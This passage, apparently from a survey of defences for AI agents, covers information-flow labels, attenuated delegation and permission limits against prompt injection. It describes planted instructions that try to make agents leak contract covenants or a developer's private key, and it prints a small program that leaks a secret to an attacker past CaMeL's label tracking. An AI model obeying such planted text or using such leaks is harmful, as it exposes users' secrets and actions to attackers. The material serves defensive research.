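FIDES avoids much of this drift by keeping some data out of the model's input. When a tool returns data whose label is not at or below the current input's label, the software stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. If an email's date is trusted and its body is not, the model sees the date and a name such as `#read_emails_0.body`. The model can use that name in a later tool call, and the software substitutes the contents just before the call runs.

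This is enough for forwarding an email but not for summarising one, because something has to read the text. FIDES gives that job to an isolated second model, which has no tools. The manager's summary then takes three calls:

1. The main model asks for the emails, and the software hides their bodies in variables.
2. The main model asks the isolated model to summarise the variables. The software puts the summary in a new variable, which it labels untrusted and secret.
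3. The main model asks to send that variable to the manager.

The main model chose the tool and the recipient with no untrusted text in its input. The monitor can therefore require trusted data for those two choices and accept an untrusted message body. The attacker's email may still cause the isolated model to write a false or empty summary, but it cannot redirect the message. The secrecy policy still applies, so the manager must be allowed to read the emails.

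### Declassification and endorsement

Some legitimate work requires a flow that the lattice forbids. Declassification, which lowers the secrecy of data, and endorsement, which raises its integrity, are deliberate exceptions for such work. Sandhu gives the example of a sanitising process that removes sensitive details from a document before releasing it. Secret data may flow to the sanitiser, and the sanitiser's output may flow to the public, but secret data may not flow to the public directly. These rules are not transitive, so they cannot be part of the lattice.

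Manual approval is one way to declassify data. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) automates the decision with an isolated model that compares an outgoing message with the protected records. In one attack, this defence cut the leak rate from 52.2% to 0.5%. Another way is to check integrity instead of secrecy. If only trusted data influenced a decision to release a secret, no outsider can have planted the request, and the monitor can treat the release as intended.

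Costa and colleagues base endorsement on limiting how much an untrusted source can convey. Suppose the user asks the agent to read three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. The main model's next call depends on whether there is a request, so it sends the isolated model a question that can be answered only with yes or no. The monitor can accept an untrusted yes in the decision to create the event because a single bit cannot hold an instruction. The isolated model then extracts the meeting details into another variable.

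FIDES includes an answer's type in its label. Yes-or-no answers are at the bottom of the order, choices from a fixed list are above them, and free text is at the top. An answer from a list of *n* options carries at most log₂ *n* bits. This limit applies to each answer separately, so ten yes-or-no answers can distinguish 1,024 cases. An attacker who answers many questions can therefore steer the agent in considerable detail, but only toward actions that are already among the main model's options.

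### What FIDES achieved and what it cost

Costa and colleagues ran FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024. The attacker knew the agent's tools. Without policy checks, a basic agent carried out 152 of the attacker's tasks. FIDES without checks carried out 21, because nothing prevented the model from opening an untrusted variable and continuing as before. With the checks on, neither agent carried out any. These counts exclude cases that AgentDojo scored as successful attacks although the monitor had blocked the call or the action broke no policy.

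The checks also blocked honest work. The next table gives the share of user tasks that GPT-4o completed when there was no attack.

| Agent | Office software | Travel | Banking | Team chat |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic, with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, no checks | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

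With checks on, FIDES scored an average of eight percentage points higher than the basic agent because it hides data. It did worse in travel, where the policies let many tools run on untrusted data anyway and GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. Using OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, raised the travel score from 41% to 68% and the average lead to 16 points, so part of the lost performance came from GPT-4o's limited ability. Much of the rest was intended, because several banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the integrity policy exists to prevent.

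The perfect security score depends on how the researchers assigned the labels. AgentDojo doesn't include labels, so Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. The labels therefore correctly identified every place where an attack could appear. A company labelling its own mailboxes and databases would not have that advantage. The experiment also left out the restriction to short answers, so it did not test endorsement by type.

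Costa and colleagues acknowledge that FIDES needs a source of labels. They infer the readers of an email from its sender and recipients, although someone may have shared it more widely. They suggest that a system might mark a document as trusted after a detector finds no injection in it, but the guarantee is then no better than the detector. For tools that nobody has labelled yet, *APPA* keeps a list of unresolved sources beside each label and allows an operation only if it would also pass once those sources had labels.

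Labels must also persist between tasks. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent on Monday to save the details of an invoice and on Tuesday to pay it. If the invoice came from an attacker, the account number is still untrusted on Tuesday. The system stores the invoice with its label and shows the model only a description until the payment runs. On AgentDojo tasks extended over several requests, attacks succeeded 0.2% of the time, but label checks cut the share of completed tasks from 62.5% to 35.3%.

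### What noninterference adds

FIDES uses taint tracking, which follows labels from one value to the next as a program runs. Costa and colleagues prove that it provides explicit secrecy, meaning that for any fixed sequence of tool calls, changing the secret data cannot change what those calls write to public places. But the secret data may determine which sequence the agent chooses, so an outsider who can see the calls may learn something about the data.

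Noninterference closes this gap by comparing whole runs. If two runs start with the same public data but different secrets, every public result must be the same in both, whichever path each run takes. For integrity, the two runs start with the same trusted data but different untrusted data, and everything with a trusted label must stay the same however the attacker rewrites the email.

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, show the difference with a leak in CaMeL, a system that Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced in 2025. CaMeL has a model write a program from the user's request and tracks labels while the program runs. It correctly refuses a program that emails an attacker if the user's balance is above some threshold. The following version, which adapts an example that Fenton published in 1974, gets through:

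```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email(attacker, "rich!")
```

CaMeL raises a variable's label only when the program actually assigns to the variable under a secret condition.

| | Balance above threshold | Balance at or below threshold |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp` after the first test | False, secret | True, public |
| `rich` after the second test | True, public | False, public |
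| Email to the attacker | Sent | Not sent |

In both cases, `rich` ends with a public label and reveals to the attacker which side of the threshold the balance is on. When the balance is high, the program skips the assignment to `rich`, so CaMeL doesn't raise the variable's label, even though skipping the assignment conveys the secret. Denning described this problem in 1976 and called it an implicit flow. One of her remedies was to have the compiler work out in advance which variables a branch could change, and raise their labels whether or not the branch runs.

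Garby and colleagues found a second leak outside the part of CaMeL that tracks labels. When a policy blocks a program, ordinary Python code prompts the model for another attempt. Whether the policy blocks a program can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of the secret, and repeated attempts can reveal all of it.

Costa and colleagues rejected full noninterference for FIDES because it would essentially forbid an agent from using any tool that might write public data after using any tool that might have read a secret.

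### Agents that write programs

CaMeL, LLMbda and Language-Based Agent Control all have the model write programs instead of proposing one tool call at a time. They differ in when the model may see untrusted data and in what has been proved about them.

In CaMeL, a privileged model writes the whole program before any tool returns data, and a second model without tools reads untrusted text while the program runs. An attacker's email therefore cannot change the sequence of steps, but it can still supply a value that a step uses, such as the account number for a payment. As Girrens and Wang explain, CaMeL records where each value came from and who may receive it, and each tool has its own policy about which values it accepts. These policies can express more than label comparisons, but the protection depends on someone writing each one correctly.

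LLMbda is a small programming language that Garby and colleagues designed for agents. Every value has a label, including the model's conversation and any code the model generates. A program may not add to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret, which prevents the conversational form of the leak in CaMeL. Garby and colleagues prove noninterference for every program in the language and have checked the proof with the Lean proof assistant. The proof covers the same interpreter that calls the model.

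A model's answers are random, so the theorem compares the probabilities of results. It also allows for runs that never finish, including those that a policy stops. Let μ and ν give the probabilities of each public result under two different secrets. The theorem guarantees a third assignment of probabilities, ω, that is at least as large as both μ and ν for every result and whose values add up to no more than one.

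Suppose an agent prints "done" 90% of the time under one secret and 60% under another, and otherwise never finishes. The theorem permits this because an ω that assigns "done" a probability of 90% covers both cases. It rules out an agent that prints "done" 90% of the time under one secret and "failed" 90% of the time under the other, because ω's probabilities would have to add up to 180%. The two sets of results can differ by no more than the average probability that a run does not finish. Secrets can therefore change the agent's public results only by affecting whether it finishes.

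LLMbda also has an explicit command for endorsement. A second theorem shows that this command cannot weaken the protection of secrets. The command does weaken integrity by design, and a careless model could endorse anything. Garby and colleagues reduce this risk by having the model write its plan, including every endorsement, before it sees outside data. The model first practises on a simulated account, where it can correct its mistakes without reading anything an attacker wrote.

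They tested this agent on AgentDojo's banking tasks with three models, and two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill according to the contents of a file, and the attacker had replaced the contents. Because the agent was doing what the user asked, labels alone could have stopped these attacks only by forbidding the task. With GPT-5.2, the agent completed 36 of 48 attempts at the user's tasks, compared with 18 for CaMeL with its policies on and 32 with them off. The comparison somewhat favors LLMbda, because its agent enforced only some of CaMeL's policies and could endorse data. When the researchers removed endorsement, the number of attempts completed with another model, Qwen3.7-plus, fell from 36 to 30.

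Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, use an existing language, Haskell, whose types record what effects a program can have. Before a generated program runs, a type checker rejects it if it could do anything outside an approved set of operations. For example, they required every entry in a bibliography to come from the computer science database DBLP. Only the database tool could create a value of the type "trusted entry", and only such values could go into the bibliography. The resulting agent invented no details in 925 citations, while an ordinary agent with web search invented details in 19 of 1,002.

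Zhou and colleagues enforce secrecy and integrity with LIO, an established Haskell library that raises a program's label as it reads data and checks the label before the program writes. A model can hand untrusted text to a second agent and receive a sealed result, as in FIDES. The second agent can keep its tools, unlike the isolated model in FIDES or CaMeL, because LIO checks that agent's calls against its own label. The researchers prove that the guarantees Haskell's types give ordinary programs also hold for programs that call agents. The information-flow guarantee comes from earlier proofs about LIO.

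In tests without an attack, every system that researchers ran both with and without enforcement completed fewer tasks with it.

| System | Tasks and model | Without checks | With checks | Tested by |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES | Team chat, GPT-4o | 63.8% | 47.6% | Costa and colleagues |
| CaMeL | Banking, GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% | Garby and colleagues |
| CaMeL | Team chat, Claude Opus 4.8 | 76% | 29% | Zhou and colleagues |
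| Language-Based Agent Control | Team chat, Claude Opus 4.8 | 76% | 43% | Zhou and colleagues |
| SPA | All AgentDojo tasks | 53.0% | 29.0% | Girrens and Wang |

The models, policies and tasks differ, so the table cannot rank the systems. But the last three rows show that the restrictions still interfere with tasks even when the models are better, because many of the tasks need an untrusted source to influence an action.

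### When the benchmark's attacks stop working

Zhou and colleagues also used AgentDojo's team-chat tasks to test whether recent models need this protection. They ran Claude Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8 and Sonnet 5, and OpenAI's GPT-5.4, against 105 attacks (21 user tasks, each paired with 5 attacker goals) in three wordings. Every model resisted all 105 attacks in every wording, even with the policies off. In that condition, CaMeL still hides untrusted text from its planning model, but Language-Based Agent Control has no information-flow checks.

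A perfect security score on these attacks is therefore no longer evidence that a defence works, because an agent with current models and no label checks gets the same score. The earlier FIDES result is more informative, since GPT-4o carried out 152 attacks without protection. Part of a good score can still come from the agent's design rather than its labels. Garby and colleagues found that 97 of the 144 task-attack pairs in the banking tasks needed a tool that the user's task would never call. An agent that fixes its plan in advance resists nearly all of those attacks without checking a label. A few banking attacks got through CaMeL with its policies off, so the perfect scores may not extend beyond the team-chat tasks.

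AgentDojo's attacks are also fixed texts, whereas a real attacker can keep revising them. Zhou and colleagues point to GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attacker, which consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. They therefore ran a harsher test that assumed the attack had already worked. Whenever an agent received a planted instruction, the software deleted the agent's real task and left only the attacker's text.

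Depending on the model, 16% to 42% of these attacks succeeded without policies, and none of the 735 attacks on each model succeeded with them. Agents completed 494 to 558 of the 735 user tasks without policies, and 294 to 351 with them.

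## Delegation: passing on authority without enlarging it

An agent with a large job often hands parts of it to other agents. The developer's coding agent might have one sub-agent read the documentation and another run the tests, and each needs some authority to do its part. Attenuation means passing on no more authority than the agent itself has. If every agent in a chain attenuates, the last one can do nothing the developer did not allow the first to do.

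### Why a chain of grants cannot grow

Wei and Xiong define attenuation for grants with four main parts:

- *C*, the effects the grant permits, such as reading certain receipts or sending a summary to Alice
- *O*, the obligations that someone must meet first, such as a manager's approval
- *X*, rules about which sources may settle a detail the grant leaves open, such as the staff directory for a manager's address
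- *Δ*, the conditions under which the grant is valid, such as an expiry time or a limit on how many more times agents may pass it on.

A child grant γ′ attenuates its parent γ, in symbols γ′ ≤ γ, when all of these hold:

- *C′* ⊆ *C*, so the child permits no new effects.
- *O* ⊆ *O′*, so the child keeps every obligation and may add more.
- *X* ⊆ *X′*, so the child also keeps every rule about sources.
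- *Δ′* ⇒ *Δ*, so the child is valid only when the parent is.

A child grant may therefore drop permissions and add obligations, but it may not add permissions or drop obligations. In Wei and Xiong's example, an assistant may prepare an expense summary and send it to Alice once a manager approves. The assistant asks a second agent to review the summary. The reviewer's grant lets it read the summary but not send it, and keeps the approval obligation.

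The proof that a chain cannot exceed its starting point is by induction. Let γ₀ be the root grant, which a person or organisation issued, and let γ₁, γ₂ and so on be the grants below it in one chain. The claim is that γₙ ≤ γ₀ for every *n*. It holds for *n* = 0, because every grant is ≤ itself. Now suppose it holds for γₙ, and the holder of γₙ issues γₙ₊₁ ≤ γₙ. Then:

- *Cₙ₊₁* ⊆ *Cₙ* ⊆ *C₀*, so the new grant permits nothing beyond the root.
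- *O₀* ⊆ *Oₙ* ⊆ *Oₙ₊₁*, so no obligation has disappeared, and the same argument covers *X*.
- *Δₙ₊₁* ⇒ *Δₙ* ⇒ *Δ₀*, so the new grant is valid only when the root is.

Hence γₙ₊₁ ≤ γ₀, and the claim holds along the whole chain. When an agent acts, the monitor permits only effects in the set *C* of the grant it presents, and all of these are in *C₀*. The argument does not depend on how the agents behave, so it holds even if an attacker controls every agent below the root.

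Two sub-agents also can't exceed the root by pooling grants that come from it. The root is above both grants, so it is above their join. This limit doesn't apply to grants from different roots, because neither root is necessarily above both grants.

An agent can pass on everything it has and still obey the rule, because every grant is ≤ itself. The theorem therefore does not require an agent to narrow a grant.

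The proof also assumes that a monitor verifies the credential for every step and checks each operation against it. The credential must list the clauses of the grant, because a bare scope such as "mail" omits the limit on recipients. The monitor must be able to evaluate those clauses and determine what effects an operation will have, and no operation may bypass the monitor.

Current protocols do not guarantee all this. Agent2Agent (A2A), a protocol through which agents from different organisations exchange tasks, identifies each agent with a signed "agent card". Wei and Xiong note that the card does not limit the authority other agents pass to that agent. According to *A2ABreak* (2026), A2A also loses track of the originating agent over several steps, so a compromised agent in the middle can keep a forwarded credential and reuse it later.

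### Credentials that holders can narrow

The oldest way to attenuate authority is with object capabilities, which are capability tokens that take the form of references to objects in a program. A holder narrows a reference by creating a second object that forwards only some requests to the first. For example, an agent with a reference to a mailbox could create a wrapper that forwards read requests and ignores send requests. The agent gives the sub-agent a reference to the wrapper, so the sub-agent can reach the mailbox only through the wrapper.

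This works where an operating system or programming language stops programs from forging references. Across a network, cryptography has to prevent forgery instead. Macaroons, which Birgisson and colleagues introduced in 2014, are credentials to which any holder can add restrictions, called caveats. They rely on HMAC, a function that turns a key and a text into a short tag. Anyone with the key can recompute the tag, but it is infeasible to forge a tag without the key or to recover the key from a tag.

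Suppose the developer's agent wants a sub-agent to push to one branch of her repository until 17:00:

1. The repository server issues the agent a credential with a tag, *t₀*, which it computed from its own secret key.
2. The agent adds the caveat "only branch fix-test" and computes *t₁* = HMAC(*t₀*, "only branch fix-test").
3. It adds "only until 17:00" and computes *t₂* = HMAC(*t₁*, "only until 17:00").
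4. It gives the sub-agent the credential with both caveats and *t₂*, but keeps *t₀* and *t₁*.

The sub-agent can use *t₂* to add a third caveat. It would need *t₁* to remove the time limit, and it cannot compute *t₁* from *t₂*. When the sub-agent pushes, the server recomputes the tags from its secret key and accepts the push only if the last tag matches and every caveat holds. The credential therefore permits only what all its caveats allow, so adding a caveat takes a meet in the permission lattice. The agent can add one without contacting the server.

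In OAuth, the standard behind most delegated access on the web, a program instead asks an authorization server to exchange its token for one with a smaller scope (IETF, *Attenuating Agent Tokens*, draft internet standard, 2026). The server enforces the reduction, but every step in a delegation chain requires another request to it. The new token may contain a nested list of the agents that acted earlier. Because the list is only informational, a service that receives the token can see which agents took part but cannot use the list to check that each step narrowed the token's scope.

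*An Attenuated Delegation Profile for Automated Agents* (Hassan, 2026) proposes sending the whole delegation chain with each request. Each link must have a narrower scope than its parent, conditions at least as strict, and a lifetime no longer than its parent's. The verifier checks every link, because the last link can be narrower than its parent and still exceed the root's authority if the parent already exceeded it.

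These checks are fast. cA2A, by Poddar, Fulkerson and Siddique, extends A2A with attenuating credentials and a verifiable record of each step. Wei and Xiong report that its developers ran attenuation checks on 5,400 generated chains and that verification took about 0.22 milliseconds per step. The system also rejected replayed credentials and chains spliced from parts of others. *AIP* (Prakash, 2026) measured a similar design in which each delegation adds 340 to 380 bytes. That design verified a five-step chain in under a millisecond and rejected all 600 attempted attacks.

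AIP attaches a small program of rules to each token and evaluates the rules at every step. *InterSAGE* (2026) instead narrows authority only by set intersection. This is simpler to verify, because a verifier only has to compare sets and check signatures, but it limits restrictions to those that can be written as sets. Wei and Xiong think the harder problem is agreeing on a vocabulary for the authority that agents pass on, since the cryptography already exists.

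### DelegateGuard and the contract summary

*DelegateGuard* (Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues, 2026) applies attenuation to an agent that summarises a confidential contract. This agent, the orchestrator, passes the formatting to a worker. Someone has planted an instruction in the contract for agents to send all its restrictive covenants to an outside web address before formatting.

A trusted component outside the model turns the user's request into the orchestrator's grant. The orchestrator may then give the worker a smaller one:

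| | Orchestrator | Formatting worker |
|---|---|---|
| Purpose | contract.summarize | contract.summarize/format |
| Data labels | contract.confidential | contract.confidential |
| Operations | read, transform, transmit, delegate | transform, transmit |
| Destinations | user.response, internal | user.response |

The monitor compares the grants row by row. The worker's purpose begins with the orchestrator's purpose followed by a slash, so it counts as narrower. Each of the worker's other entries is a subset of the orchestrator's. Each grant also has a delegation depth that must fall at every step, so no chain can go on forever.

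Now suppose the planted clause misleads the orchestrator into requesting a worker grant that includes the destination `external.webhook`. The orchestrator's own destinations are only `user.response` and `internal`. The requested set is not a subset of these, so the monitor refuses to create the grant.

The clause might instead mislead the worker after it has received the smaller grant. If the worker proposes sending the covenants to the outside address, the monitor blocks the request because that address is not among the worker's permitted destinations. The worker also can't get help from another agent with wider access, because the worker's grant leaves out the "delegate" operation. It can still return the formatted summary to the user.

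Tran-Truong and colleagues tested 45 attacks across five kinds of office work. One open model proposed the attacker's action in 42 of them and another in 44, and the monitor blocked all of these actions. In 90 multi-turn runs, the leak rate fell from 84.4% to 20%, and the agents completed all their tasks.

Attenuation cannot bring that rate to zero in general. Tran-Truong and colleagues prove that a monitor that ignores the content and quantity of data cannot prevent leaks to an authorised destination that outsiders can see. In one of their tasks, an agent that knows about an unannounced security flaw writes a review comment in a code repository. If outsiders can read the comments, the agent can reveal the flaw without exceeding its grant. Preventing this requires checking what the comment contains.

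DelegateGuard also cannot repair a root grant that is too broad. If the trusted component had listed the outside address among the orchestrator's destinations, the monitor would have approved the worker's grant.

### AGENTCAP and tokens from other sessions

A worker that serves two users may hold tokens from two roots, and an attacker in one session could try to make the worker use authority from the other. *AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) prevents this by binding each token to one agent and one session. Within a session, authority passes only from parent to child. Other agents may exchange messages with the child, but they cannot use its token.

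Each token specifies an action, a resource, a declared purpose, an expiry time and a number of permitted calls. A child token must keep the parent's action and resource. It may not permit more calls or expire later than the parent, and it must allow fewer further delegations. When the worker uses its token, a gateway follows the chain from the worker back to the root. At each step, it checks that the signature is valid, that the token obeys these limits and that nobody has revoked it. The gateway repeats these checks for every call because a chain that was valid for one call may be invalid by the next.

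Delegation cannot change a token's action or resource, so a supervisor with access to a folder cannot give a worker a token for one file in it. This rule makes verification simple, but it means more of the limits must be set in the policy that issues the first token. In the example banking policy, a token for sending money lasts 30 seconds and permits one call, so there is little left to narrow.

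With GPT-5.4, AGENTCAP reduced the success rate of attacks in both AgentDojo and InjecAgent to zero. Across all settings, the share of tasks its agents completed under attack was at most 4.18 percentage points below that of unprotected agents. Most of the label-based systems reduce task completion by much more, although the researchers wrote AGENTCAP's policies for the benchmarks' own tools and ran each condition once. These benchmarks mainly test the checks on tool calls. The evidence on delegation comes from smaller, controlled scenarios, in which AGENTCAP blocked every unauthorised operation.

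### Two agents and one purchase

Suppose a user allows an agent to book one flight, and the agent passes the job to two sub-agents. Each sub-agent's grant permits one booking, so each grant is ≤ the user's original grant. But both sub-agents book a flight, and the user pays for two.

The induction proof is correct, but it concerns only which effects a grant permits. The root permits booking a flight, and the proof places no limit on how many times that happens. A monitor can take the meet of a one-booking limit with itself any number of times and get the same limit, even though two bookings cost twice as much as one. A lattice can order spending limits, but a separate mechanism has to track the spending.

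AGENTCAP's attenuation rule has the same gap. It checks each child token's call limit separately against the parent's, so two children may each receive as many calls as the parent had.

The parent could split its $50 budget evenly between two sub-agents. This needs no further coordination, but a sub-agent that has to spend $30 then fails even if the other spends nothing. Splitting also doesn't work for a single flight, which can't be divided.

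Wei and Xiong's solution is a shared ledger with atomic reservation. An agent must reserve an amount before spending it, and the ledger checks the remaining budget and records the reservation in one indivisible step. If these were separate steps, the ledger could approve both sub-agents' requests before recording either one, and together they could overspend the budget.

| Event | Separate steps | Atomic reservation |
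|---|---|---|
| First agent asks | One booking left | One booking left, now reserved |
| Second agent asks | One booking left | None left, so the ledger refuses |
| Agents book | Two flights | One flight |

This works for any number of agents. Let *B* be the budget, *r* the amount reserved and *c* the amount spent. The ledger accepts a new reservation of *m* only if *r* + *c* + *m* ≤ *B*. If the purchase goes through, *m* moves from *r* to *c*, which leaves *r* + *c* unchanged. If the purchase fails, *m* is subtracted from *r* and the total falls. So *r* + *c* never exceeds *B*, and neither does *c*.

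Retries could still cause spending to exceed the limit. If a booking request times out, the agent may not know whether the airline received it. Each operation therefore has a fixed identifier, called an idempotency key, which the agent includes in every retry so that the airline can recognise duplicates. If the airline doesn't support these keys, it must let the system check the outcome of the first request. Until the system has confirmed that outcome, the ledger records the money as spent.

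An agent could also evade a budget by starting more tasks. If each of *n* tasks has its own budget *B*, together they can spend *nB*. Wei and Xiong also cap each user's total spending across all tasks. They propose a benchmark case in which the user's overall budget is $50 and an attacker divides a goal into tasks that each spend $5. The system should refuse to issue a grant for the eleventh task.

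An agent can narrow a Macaroon without contacting anyone, but it must reach the ledger to spend from a shared budget. If the ledger is unavailable, the monitor has to refuse the request, even when money remains. Coordination through a ledger is also less tested than attenuation. *Authorization Propagation in Agent2Agent Systems* (2026) describes a prototype that rejected 14 of 15 attack scenarios in a four-party workflow, but the experiment did not cover simultaneous replays of a request or verifiers that restart and lose their records.

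### Revoking authority while work is in flight

A user may cancel a task after its agents have passed authority to others. In DelegateGuard, revoking a grant also revokes every grant below it. A worker may still take a job from a queue after the user has cancelled the orchestrator's task. The worker's own token looks valid, so the monitor has to check every grant above the token.

A wrapper around an object capability can make access revocable. Miller and Shapiro describe a wrapper, called a caretaker, that forwards requests and has a switch that its owner keeps. When the owner turns it off, the caretaker stops forwarding requests, and every reference to it becomes useless at once.

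Revoking every permission derived from a cancelled grant can remove too much access when agents share a helper. If two orchestrators have each authorised the same reviewer, cancelling one task should not stop the other. Zhou and Zhang describe VERA, a system that revokes individual links between agents. The reviewer keeps its access as long as at least one independent chain of valid authorisations leads to it.

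A monitor may also need to reduce authority before anyone revokes it. *Agent-ZTA* (Khan and Syed, 2026) distinguishes the most that delegation allows an agent, *D*, from what the agent may use at time *t*, *E*(*t*), and requires that *E*(*t*) ⊆ *D*. Suppose agent A delegates to B, which delegates to C, and then an alarm indicates that A has been compromised. C's token is still valid, but the monitor can shrink *E*(*t*) for C's sensitive operations. An alarm about C can likewise make the monitor re-evaluate what A may do with that part of the work. If a required security report is missing, the monitor refuses the request. The paper gives worked examples but no experiments, and its design depends on a separate system to raise the alarm in time.

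AGENTCAP detects possible misuse itself by keeping a trust score for each agent. The score starts at 0.8 and is multiplied by 0.7 after each refused or suspicious call. With the default settings, the agent loses permission to write after the second such call and all permissions after the third. This stops an agent that keeps probing for gaps, but not one that does its damage in a single call.

None of these methods can undo a completed action. Wei and Xiong give each grant a version number. Revoking a grant raises its number, and the ledger then refuses new reservations under the old version. An operation in progress may still finish unless the service can cancel it. A completed purchase may be refundable, but there is no equivalent remedy for a sent email.

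The same difficulty arises with information inside the system. A sub-agent may have saved a copy of a document before losing access, and revocation does not erase that copy. A label on the copy can still limit where it goes if the sub-agent's tools enforce labels.

Wei and Xiong classify effects by how easily they can be reversed. The scale runs from reading, through changes that take effort to undo, to disclosures, physical actions and non-refundable payments. An agent may have standing permission for reversible effects, but needs fresh human approval for each irreversible one. A late revocation can still leave changes to undo, but a person will have approved any permanent effect.

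### Trusting someone with secrets but not with decisions

So far, delegation has meant handing over a smaller grant. Researchers also use the word for a declaration of trust between two parties. A single scale cannot always express this trust, because one party may trust another with its secrets but not with influence over its actions, or the reverse. The developer might let a hosted service read her private code but not let its answers decide what her agent pushes. Or she might accept an outside security scanner's verdict but show it none of her secrets.

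*An Algebraic Approach to Asymmetric Delegation and Polymorphic Label Inference* (Ren, Acay and Myers, 2025) treats trust in confidentiality and trust in integrity separately. If Alice delegates her confidentiality to Bob, he may see everything she can see. If she delegates her integrity to him, she trusts that nobody has maliciously changed the information he accepts.

The main example is a cryptography puzzle in which Alice and Bob want to know who is richer without revealing their wealth. Each trusts the other to follow the procedure, but not to see the actual figure. On a public blockchain, by contrast, everyone can see the data, but nobody trusts anyone else to follow the rules.

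Ren and colleagues arrange the parties in a lattice by authority. "Alice and Bob" stands for their combined authority, and "Alice or Bob" for the authority they have in common. (They put the greatest authority at the bottom, so combined authority is a meet, whereas in a lattice of grants it would be a join.) Each piece of data has a label with one entry for secrecy and one for integrity.

The result of comparing the two fortunes reveals something about both, so its secrecy is "Alice and Bob". Either of them could have influenced it, so its integrity is only "Alice or Bob". A program may release data only if the data is at least as trusted as it is secret. Without this rule, someone who had tampered with a value could use its release to extract secrets. The result is less trusted than it is secret, so the program can't release it to either of them.

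The programmer now declares that Alice and Bob trust each other for integrity. For that purpose the two count as equal, so:

Alice or Bob = Alice or Alice = Alice = Alice and Alice = Alice and Bob

The integrity of the result is now as high as its secrecy, and the program may release it. The two parties remain distinct for secrecy, so neither can read the other's figure.

The declaration merges elements that now have equal authority, and the merged elements still form a lattice, called a quotient lattice. It also merges differently worded rules that have the same effect. Declarations keep the program short as well. Programmers previously had to write the trust into every label and edit all of them to add a third person, Chuck, whereas declarations let them add him in two lines.

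A declaration of trust also narrows what a security proof covers. With only Alice and Bob, an attacker may control neither of them, Alice alone, Bob alone, or both. Declaring mutual trust for integrity removes the two cases in which the attacker can tamper through only one of them. Ren and colleagues prove that adding trust never makes a secure program count as insecure, because the program has to withstand fewer attackers. But if Bob tampers with the comparison while Alice is honest, the proof no longer guarantees her security.

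## Escalation by combining permitted actions

Suppose the developer's coding agent looks up the documentation for her failing test, and an attacker has planted an instruction on the page to copy her private key into the next commit. The grant permits the fetch, the read and the push individually, so the monitor allows all three and the key leaks.

Narrower delegation would not have prevented this, since no agent delegated too much authority. Data labels could have prevented it, but they also block a good deal of legitimate work. A cruder remedy is to restrict which operations an agent may combine, regardless of the data involved.

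### The lethal trifecta

The theft needed access to private data, exposure to text that an attacker could write and so use to reach the agent, and a way to send data out. Removing any one of these would have prevented it. *Lattice Guard*, the documentation of Nucleus's permission library portcullis (formerly Lattice Guard), credits this combination to the programmer Simon Willison, who called it the "lethal trifecta" in June 2025.

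An agent that cannot send data out can still do damage. If it reads web pages and edits files, an attacker can make it delete the developer's work. Meta's "Rule of Two", from October 2025, covers some of these cases because it counts any change the agent makes, as well as outside communication. Within one session, an agent may have at most two of three things: untrusted input, access to sensitive data or systems, and the power to change things or communicate. If the files count as sensitive, the file-editing agent has all three, so it must work under supervision or the developer must split the job between sessions that each start with an empty context.

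### Separation of duty and the Chinese Wall

Banks restricted combinations of permitted actions long before AI agents existed. Under separation of duty, a clerk who enters a payment may not also approve it, so fraud requires two people. Role-based systems enforce this either statically, by forbidding anyone to hold both roles, or dynamically, by letting a person hold both but use only one in a session.

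The Chinese Wall policy, which Brewer and Nash published in 1989 for financial consultants, makes access depend on which files a consultant has already opened. She may start with any bank's files, but after that she may not open those of its competitors.

Muruaga notes that these rules restrict roles and objects, while an agent does harm through combinations of tool calls, and that neither rule tracks authority passed along a chain of agents. Separation of duty also assumes that the second clerk judges the payment independently. If the developer divides the trifecta between two agents and one passes a web page's text to the other, an attacker's instruction in that text reaches both. If both agents run the same model, they may well both follow it.

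### Safe configurations

Each of the 27 configurations of reading, fetching and pushing needs one more entry, which is "ask" if a person must approve each push and "free" if not. An obligation such as approval makes a grant smaller, so ask < free. The two values double the lattice to 54 configurations.

A configuration counts as safe here if reading, fetching or pushing is set to "never", or if the last entry is "ask". An unsafe configuration sets all three operations to "low-risk" or higher and allows pushes without asking. There are 2 × 2 × 2 = 8 unsafe configurations.

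The meet of two safe configurations is always safe. Let *x* be safe and let *y* be any configuration:

- If *x* has an operation at "never", then *x* ∧ *y* has it at "never" too, because the meet takes the lower level.
- If *x* has "ask", then *x* ∧ *y* has "ask", for the same reason.

The argument does not depend on *y* being safe, so one safe limit is enough. If the organisation's limit is safe, the agent's effective permission is safe whatever the developer, the task and the role allow. Everything below a safe grant is also safe, so attenuation cannot make a safe grant unsafe.

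Joins have no such guarantee. Take the research session and the publishing session from the earlier example:

- *A* = (always, low-risk, never, free)
- *B* = (low-risk, never, low-risk, free)

*A* is safe because it cannot push, and *B* is safe because it has no web access. Their join, (always, low-risk, low-risk, free), is unsafe. An administrator who approves each session and later merges them for convenience has combined all three parts of the trifecta without approving any new operation.

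A join can also remove an approval requirement. Suppose that *B* also had web access but required approval for every push. *A* is marked "free", but this has no effect because *A* does not permit pushing. The join takes the higher entry in each position, so it combines *B*'s permission to push with *A*'s "free" and allows unapproved pushes, which neither grant allowed.

### Four ways to make a grant safe

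Let *U* be the unsafe configuration (always, low-risk, low-risk, free). Four of the safe configurations below *U* have no other safe configuration between them and *U*.

| Change to *U* | Resulting configuration | Effect on repairing the test |
|---|---|---|
| Block reading | (never, low-risk, low-risk, free) | The agent cannot see the code |
| Block fetching | (always, never, low-risk, free) | The agent works without the online documentation |
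| Block pushing | (always, low-risk, never, free) | Someone else must push the fix |
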